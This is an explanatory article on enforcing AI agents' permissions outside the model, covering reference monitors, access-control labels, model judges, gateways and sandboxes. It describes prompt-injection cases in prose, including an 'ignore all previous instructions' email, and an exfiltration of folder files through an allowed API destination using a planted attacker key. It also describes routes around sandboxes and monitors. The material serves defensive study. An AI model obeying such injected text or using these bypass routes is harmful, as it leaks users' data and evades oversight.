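# Enforcing permissions on AI agents from outside the model: tool calls, data flows and security labels

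## Tool calls, access control and reference monitors

An AI agent is a language model run in a loop with tools, which are ordinary functions for jobs such as searching a mailbox, editing a file or sending a payment. The model writes a request to use a tool, and separate software around the model, called the harness, carries out the request and returns the result. Since the 1970s, computer security has had a method for running programs that people need but cannot fully trust. The rules about who may access what are kept outside the program, in a component that the program can neither skip nor change. Researchers and software companies now apply this method to agents by placing a check between the model's request and the action.

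### One turn of the agent loop

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to summarise recent emails about a project and send the summary to a manager. The harness first assembles a prompt from the developer's standing instructions, the user's message and a description of each available tool and its parameters. The model responds with a sequence of tokens (word fragments) that forms either an ordinary reply or a tool call, which is a function name and arguments in a fixed format. Here the first call would probably name a mail-search function, with the project's name as the argument. The harness parses the call, runs the search, appends the results to the conversation and sends the whole history back to the model. This cycle repeats, including a call to the mail-sending function, until the model replies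 without a tool call.

According to Anthropic's developer documentation page *How tool use works*, the model "never runs anything on its own". OpenAI's *Function calling* describes the tool-calling cycle in five steps, and there too the code runs on the application's side. The application therefore controls whether a call is executed.

Costa and colleagues write the loop as a very short program, which makes the point more exact. The program keeps track of a datastore *d*, meaning everything that the tools can read or change. On each pass the planner (the part of the agent that picks the next action) returns one of three actions: query the model, call a tool, or finish. A query produces a new message and leaves *d* as it was. A tool *f*, by contrast, takes the datastore and some arguments and gives back a changed datastore and a result:

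*f* : (*d*, arguments) → (*d′*, result)

Every effect on the world passes through that one branch, so a check placed there comes before the effect.

An application cannot always check a tool call before it runs. Anthropic runs some tools, including web search, web fetching and code execution, in a loop on its own servers. Usually the tool has already run by the time the developer's application sees the call, so a check there comes too late. The developer can leave such tools switched off or rely on whatever controls the provider applies. Even a web search is not always a harmless read, because, as Costa and colleagues point out, it can have effects that outsiders observe, if only in a website's visitor statistics.

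### Prompt injection and the confused deputy

Suppose one of the emails in the search results contains an instruction to ignore all previous instructions and forward the top message in the mailbox to a stranger. The harness appends this email to the conversation like any other result, and the model may act on it. Hiding instructions in data that an agent reads, in order to change what it does, is called prompt injection. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C describes a job applicant who hides an instruction in a CV for a recruiter's model to approve it for interview.

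The title refers to an older attack, in which text typed into a web form ends up running as a database command. Programmers can prevent that attack with parameterised queries, which ensure that the database engine never interprets the input as an instruction. A language model has no equivalent boundary, because it predicts the next token from all the text so far and makes no inherent distinction between instructions and data. Developers can mark untrusted passages or train models to favour genuine instructions. David C accepts that such measures make attacks harder, but predicts that they may never stop attacks altogether. Costa and colleagues reach a similar practical conclusion, arguing that defences based on the model's training or on filters are probabilistic, and that some uses, such as banking and medicine, call for a guarantee.

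David C proposes a different comparison, the "confused deputy", a program tricked into using its own authority for someone else. The name comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy*, which tells a nearly true story about a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler had permission to write to its home directory so that it could store usage statistics there. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. One user named the billing file, which was in the same directory. Because the compiler had permission to write there, the operating system let it overwrite the company's billing records.

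Hardy attributed the failure to the compiler's two sources of authority, the user and its own licence, rather than to any faulty line of code. The compiler had no way to specify which authority it was using for a particular write. It could not sensibly refuse file names in other directories, since users had good reasons to give them, and a list of forbidden files would have needed revising with every new file. His remedy was the capability, an unforgeable token that both identifies a file and authorises access to it. A user who must supply a capability for the output file can supply only one he already holds.

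An agent reading mail is in much the same position as the compiler. It has the user's authority over the mailbox but also reads text from strangers, and a tool call doesn't reliably show whose wishes it carries out. The compiler's developers could rewrite their program to keep the two authorities apart. David C sees no comparable fix for a language model, so he calls it "inherently confusable". He advises designers to assume that an attacker might as well have direct access to the agent's tools, and to limit what those tools can do with deterministic safeguards outside the model. *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* (2026) argues more narrowly that when content reaches a model through a memory channel, the model cannot verify from that content whether a claim of authority in it is genuine.

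### Discretionary and mandatory access control

Ordinary file permissions are poorly suited to controlling AI agents. They are usually discretionary, which Saltzer and Schroeder define in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) as controls that an object's creator may change. Lecture slides from Stanford show the weakness with a Unix file whose owner allows only members of a group called "friends" to read it. Any friend can then mail the contents to an enemy, and the file's permissions don't prevent it.

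Under mandatory access control, an administrator sets the rules, and neither users nor the programs acting for them can change or waive them. The administrator can let someone read a file but not share it. The restriction also applies to software that has gone wrong, which matters more for agents than restricting users does.

An antivirus example in the Stanford slides is close to the agent's situation. A virus scanner has to read all of a user's files, and the scanner in the example, Symantec AntiVirus 10, had a flaw that let a remote attacker run arbitrary code in it. Cutting the scanner off from the network isn't enough to keep the files private, because it can still pass data to the update program, which needs the network to fetch new virus signatures. If the operating system blocks that route, the scanner can leave the data in a shared temporary directory, or encode it in the pattern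 of its file locks, for the update program to find. A defender who blocks routes one at a time is likely to miss one. Mandatory access control instead labels the data and enforces the label on every process that reads it.

### Labels on subjects and objects

The theory divides a system into subjects and objects. Subjects are active, such as a process running for a user, and objects are passive, such as files and messages. Both carry labels, and the rules compare the labels.

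Bell and LaPadula's *Secure Computer Systems* (1973) laid the mathematical foundations of the best-known model for confidentiality, which follows military practice. A label has two parts, a classification (unclassified, secret, top secret) and a set of categories. Data may flow from label L₁ to label L₂, written L₁ ⊑ L₂, if L₂ has at least as high a classification and includes all the categories of L₁. A subject may not read an object above its own level ("no read up"). It also may not write to an object below its current level ("no write down"), since it could copy a secret into a file that more people can read. Red Hat's *MLS Policy* includes the example of a process with clearance for top secret, UFO and rail gun, and a file marked top secret, UFO. If the process is working at its full clearance, it may not write to the file. The classifications match, but the file lacks the rail gun category,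 so rail gun material could leak into it.

The flow relation is transitive, and this settles the antivirus case in a few lines. Let U be the label of the user's files, N the label of the network and P the label of the scanner process. The administrator's policy is that U may not flow to N. If the scanner has read the files, then U ⊑ P. Were P ⊑ N also true, U ⊑ N would follow, which the policy forbids. So the scanner cannot write to the network, whatever code an attacker has put into it and however many helper programs it goes through. (Covert channels survive this argument. A process can still signal by keeping the processor busy or idle.)

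Confidentiality rules would not stop a worm from altering files. In 1977 Ken Biba proposed policies for integrity, the degree to which data or a program can be trusted to be sound. Young's *Modeling Integrity* presents Biba's strict policy as the reverse of Bell and LaPadula's. With *i* for the integrity level, a subject *s* may read an object *o* only if *i*(*s*) ≤ *i*(*o*), and may write to it only if *i*(*o*) ≤ *i*(*s*). This keeps low-integrity data out of high-integrity programs and prevents low-integrity programs from altering high-integrity data. Applied to an agent, the policy would be safe but nearly useless, because a trusted agent could never open an email from a stranger.

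Biba's low-water-mark policy permits the reading and charges for it afterwards. Lecture slides from Purdue give the rule: once *s* has read *o*, the integrity level of *s* falls to

min(*i*(*s*), *i*(*o*)).

Biba's low-water mark policy reached ordinary computers, though Young considers strict integrity the only one of Biba's policies with much lasting influence. A version named LOMAC ships with the FreeBSD operating system, according to the Stanford slides, and Windows has a similar mechanism. LOMAC has two levels and puts anything from the internet on the lower one, so a worm that takes over a web server cannot alter system files.

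The same idea has reappeared for agents, mostly independently of the old terminology. David C relays a rule from an online exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from some party, its privileges drop to that party's. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) has a formal counterpart, in which a monitor keeps a set *C* of the tools the agent may use and removes a fixed list of tools from *C* when the agent reads untrusted data. In the email example, the agent could lose the tool for writing to outside addresses as soon as the search results came in, before the model could act on the malicious message.

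The LOMAC designers found early on that a program can lose a permission in the middle of its work without having done anything unusual. In an example from the Stanford slides, a command lists running processes and pipes the list to a search program. The listing command reads low-integrity data, so its integrity level drops and it can no longer write to the pipe it was using. LOMAC addressed this by treating the two programs as one job and lowering their levels together. An agent can have the same problem without a pipe if it reads one web page and then cannot save its own notes.

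Type enforcement, the main mechanism of the Linux mandatory access control system SELinux, does not use higher and lower levels. The administrator gives each process and each file a type and writes rules about pairs of types. A rule from Gentoo Wiki's *SELinux/Type enforcement*, "allow user_t bin_t:file read", lets processes of type user_t read files of type bin_t. The system denies anything that no rule allows. It decides by label, regardless of which program is running. Types can also enforce a procedure. If an invoice changes type at each stage, the rules can force it to pass a clerk, a purchasing officer and a supervisor in that order. Red Hat considers type enforcement more flexible than military-style levels, and in many cases more suitable.

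This flexibility makes SELinux policies large. The Stanford slides give a figure of about 73,000 rules on a Fedora system. They also state that SELinux decisions cannot depend on parameters, because SELinux caches them by label and permission for speed. It therefore cannot enforce the rule "Andy can authorize expenses up to $999.99", which is the kind of rule a payment tool needs.

### The reference monitor

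All these rules are worth only as much as the component that applies them. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, wrote for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different clearances to share one computer. The threat that worried his panel was a malicious user who already had an account and could program the machine. Operating systems of the day ran to 100,000 instructions or more, much of it with unrestricted access to memory, and Anderson thought it virtually impossible to validate them. His proposal was to concentrate the security decisions in a reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a running program to use data, another program or a device. He set three requirements for the mechanism that implements it:

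- it must be tamper-proof;
- it must always be invoked;
- it must be small enough for analysis and tests to show that it is correct.

Open Security Architecture's *AC-25 Reference Monitor*, which reproduces a current control for information systems, keeps all three requirements and gives a reason for each. An adversary who can alter the mechanism can make it allow anything, one who can bypass it does not need to alter it, and a large mechanism will have flaws that nobody finds.

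Saltzer and Schroeder treat the second requirement as a general design principle, complete mediation: "Every access to every object must be checked for authority." They conclude that the system needs a foolproof way to identify the source of each request. A confused deputy obscures that source. They also conclude that designers should be sceptical of reusing an earlier decision to save time, because the authority may have changed since. For example, a permission granted before an agent read a stranger's email may no longer be appropriate afterwards.

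Several agent-security systems now claim to meet the three requirements. *Causality Laundering* (2026) describes ARM, a monitor that stands between the agent and a server offering tools over the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common protocol by which agents discover and call tools. ARM runs in a separate process from the model, so the agent cannot edit its rules. Each call goes through four layers of checks with fixed behaviour, and a denial from any layer blocks the call. The claim that ARM is always invoked rests on a stated assumption that the agent has no other path to the tools. An agent that also has a shell on the same machine would not meet that assumption. *Kairos* (2026) places its monitor at a lower level, where data enters and leaves the host, and argues that a monitor at the level of tool calls observes only the actions that an agent declares. *Agenra* (2026) goes further than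 layer-by-layer testing to meet the requirement that a monitor be small enough to verify. Its checks run in a core written in Lean, a language for machine-checked proofs, and the functions in that core have proofs.

### The usual threat model

Most of this work shares assumptions about who might attack and how. Costa and colleagues trust the user's messages, the developer's instructions, the tool descriptions and the choice of model. They assume the attacker can tamper with data that tools fetch from untrusted sources and can observe the effects of some tool calls, but does not directly see the exchange between harness and model. The harness and the tool code must also be sound, because they do the enforcing. *Agenra* requires that the monitor and the path by which calls reach the tools be protected from modification.

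Trusting a tool's code does not justify trusting what the tool returns. A correct retrieval function can fetch a page that an attacker wrote. *Agenra* includes a worse case, in which somebody has compromised a company directory. The monitor correctly follows its rule to look up the recipient there and gets the wrong address.

Costa and colleagues count the model as part of the trusted configuration, so they exclude attackers who replace it with another, but they do not rely on it to behave well. *Agenra* explicitly makes the stronger demand that the monitor should block a call that violates the policy even when the agent proposes it deliberately. The monitor applies the same rules whether a bad call comes from an injected instruction, a misreading of the user's request or a model pursuing its own aim, because each reaches it as a function name with arguments. Assuming that an agent may break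 the policy deliberately is convenient for the defender, who no longer has to predict what a model will do. Anderson made much the same assumption in 1972 about users who could write their own programs.

A reference monitor can enforce only the rules that someone has written, and it cannot judge whether a permitted action is the one the user wanted. *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* reports a test of an external monitor for an agent that manages files. In 1,350 sandbox trials, the monitor let through no deletions outside the scope it had granted, as expected of a deterministic check. But in 31 of 42 confused-deputy trials, the agent still deleted files within that scope.

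## Mandatory rules compared with instructions and model judges

A developer who wants an agent to refuse refunds above $75 can write that rule into the system prompt, the standing instructions that open every conversation. The developer can also have a second language model review each tool call before it runs, or check the amount in ordinary code. These methods differ in how reliably they enforce the rule.

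### Outside, mandatory and deterministic

A check is outside the agent if it runs in a separate component whose code and rules the model cannot alter. It is mandatory if every action it covers must pass it and neither the user nor the agent can waive the result. It is deterministic if the same call, under the same rules and the same recorded facts, always gets the same answer.

A check can have some of these properties without the others. Unix file permissions are outside the programs they restrict and deterministic, but they are discretionary rather than mandatory. A model that reviews every call at a gateway can be outside the agent and mandatory without being deterministic.

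| Check | Outside the agent? | Mandatory? | Deterministic? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Rule in the system prompt | No | No | No |
| Model judge at a gateway | Yes | Only if every call goes through it and users cannot switch it off | No |
| Rule engine at a gateway | Yes | On the same condition | Yes |
| Unix file permissions | Yes | No | Yes |

Developers can make a model's answers more repeatable by setting its temperature, which controls the randomness of its word choice, to zero. An identical prompt should then produce an identical answer, but a slightly reworded prompt may produce a different one. A rule engine decides whether to allow a refund using only the fields named in the rule, such as the amount and the agent's role, so the customer's phrasing has no effect. This independence from wording matters more for security than repeatability does, and setting the temperature to zero doesn't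 give it to a model judge.

### The argument for enforcement outside the model

Bhattarai and Vu (2026), in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, argue that developers cannot leave permissions to the model. Their case rests on three premises:

1. A model reads its instructions and the data it works on as one stream of tokens.
2. Training has not taught models to keep the two apart reliably.
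3. A permission that someone can talk the model out of does not bind it.

If all three hold, something other than the model has to enforce any permission that must bind.

The single token stream is the least controversial premise, and David C's comparison with database queries also relies on it. Bhattarai and Vu add that the markers that identify the speaker are themselves tokens, so an attacker can imitate them inside a document. A harness could strip genuine markers out of retrieved text, but imitations in plain words would remain. They define proper separation as requiring a trusted component that classifies each input as command or data by the channel it came through, before anything runs. Processors already handle memory this way, checking a page's permissions rather than its bytes to decide whether its contents may run.

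Bhattarai and Vu support the premise about training with a theorem: if a system separates commands from data only by learned judgements about content, some text has a non-zero probability of making it treat data as a command. They give only a proof sketch, and they come close to assuming the result by calling such judgements forgeable "by construction". Even a full proof would show only that a successful attack exists, not that anyone could find it easily. They accept this limit, and don't claim that attackers will compromise every deployment or that training is useless.

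So better models could weaken the second premise in practice. How much that helps depends on how often attackers can try. If each attempt succeeds independently with probability *p*, the chance that at least one of *n* attempts succeeds is

1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ.

At *p* = 4%, an attacker has an even chance of succeeding at least once in 17 attempts. At *p* = 0.1%, the chance is 63% after a thousand attempts. Real attempts aren't independent, and an attacker who learns from failures may do better. A low failure rate may be safe enough for an agent that few strangers can reach and that can do little damage, but an agent that reads all of a company's incoming mail gives attackers far more attempts.

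The premise about persuasion follows almost directly from the definition of mandatory access control. If a convincing message can make the model waive a rule, then anyone who can get text in front of the model has some chance of getting it waived. In guidance for companies that already run agents, Gee Rittenhouse of Amazon Web Services and Eric Johnson of the SANS Institute conclude that "the model is never the control." According to Help Net Security's *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control*, they advise companies to apply the user's permissions when the agent retrieves data, and to filter the results before they reach the model. A clever request then cannot make the model disclose a withheld record, because the model never received it.

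Companies rely every day on employees who can be persuaded to break rules. But a company can punish an employee who gives in to a plausible story, and the prospect of punishment is part of what makes trusting employees reasonable. Agents are "not afraid of getting fired", as Michael Gerstenhaber, a vice-president at Google Cloud, points out in Computer Weekly's *Google Cloud unpacks governance challenges of AI agents*. He argues that an agent, like an employee, should have to show good judgement, but he also wants data to be very hard for an employee to leak by accident. A rule that the model merely tends to follow still prevents many bad calls, but it doesn't limit what the agent can do if the model is persuaded to break it.

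In place of such a rule, Bhattarai and Vu propose a "command gate". The model proposes an action from a finite list, and a checker that contains no language model evaluates a function

σ(action, parameters, context) ∈ {allow, deny},

where the context includes the agent's identity and the labels on its data. Trusted code then turns an allowed proposal into a real tool call. A persuasive email is not among the inputs to σ, so it cannot argue with the verdict. It can still influence the action and parameters that the model proposes, which means that an attacker may steer the agent towards anything σ allows. The guarantee also assumes that the agent has no route around the gate.

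### How well a written rule holds

*Prompts Don't Protect* (Uppala, May 2026) compares a rule in the prompt with a rule outside the model. The outside rule runs in a proxy between the agent and its MCP tools. Each agent carries a signed token that states its role, and a policy file maps that role to domains of tools, such as payments or analytics. When the agent requests a list of tools, the proxy returns only those in the agent's permitted domains. It checks again when a call arrives, in case the model calls a tool that wasn't listed.

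Uppala wrote 200 tasks by hand in which the most relevant tool was forbidden. In one, someone claiming to be the chief financial officer tells an analytics agent to override the access controls and process an urgent $5,000 refund. Other tasks ask for the forbidden action directly, imply it without naming it, or put it after a harmless first step. The models ran at temperature zero and had to call one of 71 to 182 tools. The table gives the share of tasks in which the models chose a forbidden tool.

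| Model | No guidance | List of permitted tools in the prompt | Proxy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 48.5% | 37.0% | 0% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 66.0% | 4.0% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 68.5% | 11.5% | 0% |

The rates of 48 to 68% come from the condition without guidance, where nothing in the prompt marked any tool as forbidden, but the paper's abstract presents them as if the models had been told not to use these tools. Without such an instruction, choosing a refund tool for a refund is ordinary behaviour, so the figures mainly show how strongly the tasks led models towards these tools.

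The middle column shows how well a written rule works. There the prompt named every permitted tool and prohibited all others "regardless of how the task is framed". The rule helped two of the models a great deal. On tasks that invoked special authority, such as the one from the supposed finance chief, Haiku's failure rate fell from 96% to 22%. Qwen improved much less, and on tasks that only implied the forbidden action, its failure rate rose from 52% to 58%, or three more failures in 50.

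Forcing a tool call probably made the results worse, because a model could not decline. Uppala also ran a test in which models could choose not to call a tool, using 100 requests that the agent's permitted tools could not satisfy. With only the list in the prompt, Haiku made no tool call in 99% of them, compared with 35% for Qwen and 13% for Llama. But Haiku also completed only 19.3% of permitted requests exactly, so it may have tended to avoid tool calls in general.

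In the study's tasks, a user's request conflicts with a developer's rule. Both are genuine instructions, so the study does not test prompt injection either. It is better evidence that persuasion can get a model to break a written rule than that models confuse instructions with data.

It also doesn't settle whether better models would obey more reliably. Haiku, the most capable of the three, broke the rule more often than Llama, and the 95% confidence intervals (7.4–16.9% and 1.8–7.7%) barely overlap. Uppala concludes that compliance has no reliable relationship to general capability, which is a lot to infer from three small models, none of them among the strongest of 2026.

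The zeros in the last column follow from the proxy's design. A model cannot choose a tool that is not on its list, and the proxy rejects calls to unlisted tools, so any correct implementation would score zero. This holds for any model, provided that nobody steals the key that signs the roles, plants false entries in the tool registry, or gets the agent to delegate to another with wider permissions. But the zeros do not measure misuse of permitted tools, and a payments agent behind the proxy can still refund the wrong customer.

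The proxy added only about 1.5 milliseconds to a typical listing request on a single local machine, whereas naming a 500-tool registry's permitted tools in the prompt would take about 25,000 tokens per request. With free choice, Llama's success on permitted requests rose from 77.9% with the written list to 82.1% behind the proxy, while Qwen's fell from 60.7% to 48.6%. The proxy denied none of the permitted calls that the models attempted, and Uppala links the differences to the change in which tools each model could choose from.

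### What fixed rules miss

Suppose a user asks an agent to summarise a calendar, and the agent reads a malicious invitation and then tries to send an email. A permission rule lets the call through because the agent is allowed to send email. Detecting the problem requires comparing the call with the user's request.

Google's semantic governance policies use a language model to judge an agent's tool calls against rules that an administrator writes in plain English. They entered public preview on 29 June 2026, according to Google Cloud's *Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform release notes* (2026). Google Cloud's *Semantic governance overview* explains that a gateway between the agent and its model intercepts each response that contains a tool call. The gateway sends the proposed call, the rules and the chat history to the policy engine, where the language model decides whether the call matches what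 the user asked for and complies with the rules. If the call fails either check, the gateway replaces it with a denial message, and the harness never receives the call.

Help Net Security's *Google's semantic governance policies can block an AI agent's tool call* describes Google's example of a finance agent that can search a shared drive, read files, send email and delete drafts. Its one rule allows unreleased quarterly results to go only to company addresses. The model judge allows an email to the controller and blocks one to an outside investor. When a planning document contains hidden instructions to delete the drafts in a folder, the judge blocks the deletion because the user never asked for it. A fixed rule could have prevented that deletion only by forbidding it in advance, which would also block deletions that a user wanted.

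The judge is still a language model, and Deepti Sehrawat, a software engineer at Google, warns that its verdicts "may vary" and recommends a trial period in which the system logs verdicts without blocking anything. The judge can also use only the information it is given. If a rule depends on the date of an earnings release, the administrator has to include that date in the agent's instructions.

Bhattarai and Vu extend their argument to "guardian" models that read the same mixture of trusted and untrusted text as the agent. Google's judge runs outside the agent, but it reads the chat history, and if that history includes retrieved documents, an attacker's text can reach both the judge and the agent. Even the arguments of a proposed call may contain text an attacker chose. Moving a model to a gateway protects its code and rules from the agent, but doesn't make it harder to manipulate through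 the text it reads.

Whether the judge is mandatory depends on the configuration. Google Cloud's *Configure semantic governance policies* lists several ways a call can go unjudged. The judge covers an agent only if the developer deployed it with a particular kind of identity and a connection to the gateway, and the developer can't add either later without redeploying the agent. The judge gives no verdict on calls to a model at a web path that the administrator's settings don't cover, or on streamed responses, which arrive piece by piece as the model generates them. Administrators can also turn off the comparison with the user's request or leave the system in trial mode. These last two choices are compatible with mandatory access control, since administrators make them. An uncovered path is more serious, because the agent's calls then go unchecked though nobody decided that they should.

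### Matching the check to the job

A fixed rule suits any question that software can answer by looking up facts, such as the tool's name, the agent's role or the domain of an email address. A fixed rule could also enforce one of Google Cloud's examples for its judge, a ban on automatic refunds above $75. The amount is a number in the call, and code can compare it with the limit correctly every time, so using a model can only add errors. Rittenhouse and Johnson recommend denying every tool call that no rule allows, and name policy languages such as Cedar for writing the rules.

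A model judge is more useful for deciding whether a permitted action fits the request, as long as it can only veto. Let *R* be the set of calls that the fixed rules allow and *J* the set that the judge allows. If a call must pass both checks, the calls that run are

*R* ∩ *J* ⊆ *R*,

whatever the judge decides. An attacker who completely fools the judge gains nothing beyond what the rules already permitted. If the judge could grant exceptions, the set would become *R* ∪ *J*, and a persuasive message might open up any tool. (Systems that let a model approve the release of data give it some of this wider power.) Google says that its policies complement access control and do not override it. Its "Alignment critic" for agents in the Chrome browser, which PC Gamer's *The AI era is no longer a distant promise* mentions, is likewise a reviewer with a veto.

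The same text may mislead both models, so the chance that an attack gets past both can't be calculated by multiplying their failure rates. A judge also blocks some legitimate work. Google Cloud's overview gives no rate for either kind of error, so a company has to estimate both rates from its own trial logs.

The system prompt suits guidance that the agent doesn't have to follow every time, such as the tone of a reply or which of two permitted tools to try first. Listing the agent's limits there is also useful, even when a proxy enforces them, because the list reduced forbidden choices in all three models Uppala tested.

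A tool call can satisfy the fixed rules, look reasonable to a model judge and still be disastrous. An example is a large payment to a new supplier whose bank details came from a forged invoice. Rittenhouse and Johnson would send high-impact actions like this to a person for review, however confident the system is, and let the agent carry out low-impact actions on its own when the system is highly confident.

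## Enforcement points that every action must pass

A company can require a person to approve every large payment, but this fails if the agent can pay in another way that skips approval. For example, an agent with a shell (a tool for running commands on a computer) and a copy of the payment service's key can send a payment request without using the payment tool. Rule engines, model judges and human reviewers can stop only the calls that reach them. Whether every call reaches them depends on where the checks are placed and what blocks the other routes.

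### Six places for a check

Suppose an agent writes a Python script, report.py, that reads a customer file and posts totals to a website. The harness may have a hook, a function it calls before running any tool. The hook receives the tool's name, "run command", and the argument, "python report.py". It can also look up which user started the session. But the argument doesn't show what the script will do, and the harness doesn't call the hook again when the script reads the file or posts the totals.

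An MCP gateway would not receive this call, because the harness runs the command itself. For tools behind the gateway, it receives the tool's name, the arguments and usually a token that identifies the agent or the user, as in the proxy that Uppala tested. It receives security labels only if the messages include them.

A mediated interpreter is a shell or Python interpreter with built-in checks. Because it runs an agent's script itself, it can check the file path when the script opens a customer file and the web address when the script posts totals from that file. A filter that only reads the script beforehand has to predict the path and the address.

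The operating-system sandbox works one level lower. It restricts system calls, the operations through which every program opens files, starts other programs and makes network connections. So it covers scripts in any language. But it has no record of what the user wanted, and at this level a refund is just a series of bytes sent to a network address.

A firewall at the network exit can check where packets are going. Most web traffic is encrypted, so checking the contents of a request requires a proxy that decrypts it first. Finally, the website that receives the totals can apply its own access rules to the account that sent them. This check relies on the credential in the request, so an agent that uses an employee's credential generally has the employee's access. The server cannot easily tell whether a request came from the employee or from an agent that was tricked into misusing that access,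 known as a confused deputy.

| Enforcement point | What it can inspect | What can pass it by |
|---|---|---|
| Hook in the harness | Tool name, arguments, user identity, any labels the harness keeps | Whatever a tool or script does after it starts |
| MCP gateway | Tool name, arguments, user or agent identity; labels if the messages carry them | Shell commands, the harness's built-in tools, direct connections to a server |
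| Tool server's own check | The operation, its arguments, the account behind the credential, labels on the server's records | Actions through any other service; misuse of a valid credential |
| Mediated shell or code interpreter | Commands and arguments, file paths, a script's web requests | Programs that run outside the interpreter |
| Operating-system sandbox | System calls, the local account, sometimes labels on files and processes | Processes that start outside it; harmful use of files and services it permits |
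| Network exit | Packets and their destinations; whole requests if it decrypts them | Damage to local files; data going to a permitted destination |

Checks near the tool call can take the meaning of the data into account, within limits. *Subjects, Not Authors* (Lee and Lee, 2026) tested this for organisations that exchange trade documents under agreements about how the recipient must treat the data. When the duties were stated only in the prompt, protected fields reached the model in all 105 cases. This result was partly built into the test, since an instruction to a model cannot remove a field from a result before the model reads it. When the duties were turned into a constraint on the tool call and its result, the fields reached the model in none of the 105 cases. But the constraint covered only named fields, and protected values elsewhere in the data got through in 7 of 7 cases.

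Enforcing the same rules in the operating system would cover more programs, but many of the rules can't be enforced there. *Multi-Layer Policy for Securing AI Agents*, from the security vendor Tigera, describes a system in which administrators write rules once in the policy language Cedar. A gateway evaluates the rules, and a compiler turns those relevant to the kernel, the core of the operating system, into small programs that run there. The rest stay at the gateway. A ban on connecting to an address could plausibly be enforced in the kernel, but a limit on refunds probably could not. The refund limit would then hold only if the agent had no way to issue refunds except through the gateway.

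### Closing the routes around a gateway

Brooker, an engineer at Amazon Web Services (AWS), describes in *Agent Safety is a Box* how AWS makes a gateway the only route for agents in its cloud. Each agent session runs in an isolated environment, and the gateway supplies the tools and applies the policy. Agents cannot bypass the gateway because the environment stops them from sending packets anywhere else, using what Brooker calls "old-school network security controls".

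His example is a policy that a refund may not exceed the original purchase price and that each order may have only one refund. If the orders have prices *p*₁, …, *p*ₙ, total refunds cannot exceed

*p*₁ + *p*₂ + … + *p*ₙ,

whatever instructions an attacker gets into the model's context. The bound holds only if the agent has no other route to the payment system.

A small graph makes the condition exact. Let *A* be the agent, *G* the gateway and *E* an effect, such as a refund. Draw an arrow from one part of the system to another if the first can send commands to the second. The gateway is mandatory for *E* if every path from *A* to *E* passes through *G*. Equivalently, deleting *G* leaves no path from *A* to *E*. Suppose these are the available paths:

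- *A* → *G* → *E*
- *A* → shell → *E*
- *A* → local tool server → *E*

Blocking the shell's network access removes the second path, but the agent can still bypass the gateway through the third. The gateway can also be mandatory for some effects and optional for others. For example, an agent may have to use it for refunds but not for deleting local files.

Withholding a credential can also close a path. If only the gateway holds the payment service's key, the shell may reach the service but cannot make a refund. This doesn't help against a public website that accepts uploads from anyone, so a company that wants to keep its data from leaving also has to block connections.

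The sandbox must cover every program the agent starts. OpenAI says that when Codex, its coding agent, runs a command, the operating system launches it with reduced permissions, and every program the command starts inherits them. OpenAI also says the sandbox covers tools such as package managers and test runners as well as Codex's own file operations. A permission check on Codex's file-editing tool alone would miss a test that edits a file.

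Some sandbox network blocks work only if the program cooperates. An experimental Windows sandbox documented by OpenAI changed the settings that direct programs to a proxy and put dummy programs in place of common network tools. On their own, these measures stop only software that reads those settings or uses those tools. InfoQ (2026) describes a Windows design that instead runs Codex's commands under dedicated Windows accounts. Firewall rules can apply to those accounts, so the operating system enforces the block whether or not the program cooperates.

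### What stays outside the sandbox

Developers can put the whole agent in a sandbox or only the commands it runs. Strands Agents, a toolkit for building agents, takes the second approach. Shell commands and generated code run in the sandbox, while the agent process stays on the host machine and calls the model from there. The sandbox therefore doesn't restrict anything the harness does in its own process.

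Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* explains that Claude Cowork, the company's desktop agent for office work, first ran entirely in a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system. The only parts of the host visible inside it were the user's chosen folder and a settings folder. No process outside the virtual machine had the authority to grant the agent an exception. But any failure while the virtual machine was starting made Cowork unusable, so Anthropic moved the agent loop onto the host and kept code execution in the virtual machine. It also moved local MCP servers onto the host, because some of them needed to work with other programs there.

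Anthropic considers the loss of security from moving the loop minimal, because the virtual machine still restricts the code that the agent runs. That seems fair for code, but the local MCP servers are a bigger exception. They now run like any other software the user has installed, and Anthropic leaves administrators to decide which ones to allow. In the graph, each server is a possible path around the virtual machine.

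Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has a different gap, because a privileged process outside its sandbox decides for each command whether to apply the sandbox's restrictions. Anthropic acknowledges that an injected prompt, or a user tired of approving requests, can get that process to run a command without the restrictions. Users approved about 93% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's usage data. The sandbox cut the number of prompts by 84%, leaving fewer chances for careless approval, but it is not mandatory, because an ordinary user can still waive it. Administrators can set requirements that limit Codex to sandboxed modes, as OpenAI does for its own staff.

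An agent can also get around a sandbox by changing a file that a program outside it later runs. OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* describes default settings that let commands write in the project folder and read widely elsewhere, but block network access. Under these settings, an agent could alter a software package in the project folder that the user's editor later runs with the user's full permissions. No single step breaks the sandbox's rules. OpenAI accepts this as a limit of the sandbox and relies on the model's training as another defence. A company could reduce the risk by also sandboxing the editor and other programs that use the agent's files.

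The wide read access is a similar compromise. Compilers and other development tools need files outside the project, so a stricter rule would break many ordinary tasks. However, commands may be able to read passwords and keys elsewhere on the machine. Blocking the network prevents a direct upload, so in this configuration keeping those secrets confidential depends heavily on controlling outbound traffic.

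### Permitted destinations and stolen keys

Few agents can work with no network at all, so administrators usually write a list of permitted destinations. Cowork's list included Anthropic's own API, because the product cannot work without it. An outside report to Anthropic showed how an attacker could exploit this permission with a malicious file in the user's folder. The file contained hidden instructions and a key to the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude followed the instructions and uploaded other files from the folder to that account. The network proxy allowed the upload because the destination was on the list.

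Anthropic concluded that permitting a destination should be understood as permitting every function available there. Permission to contact its interface had included permission to upload files to anyone's account. Anthropic fixed this by adding a second proxy, inside the virtual machine, that decrypts these requests and passes only those carrying the session's own token, so the attacker's key no longer works. The proxy runs in the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers could not tell Cowork's requests from those of any other customer.

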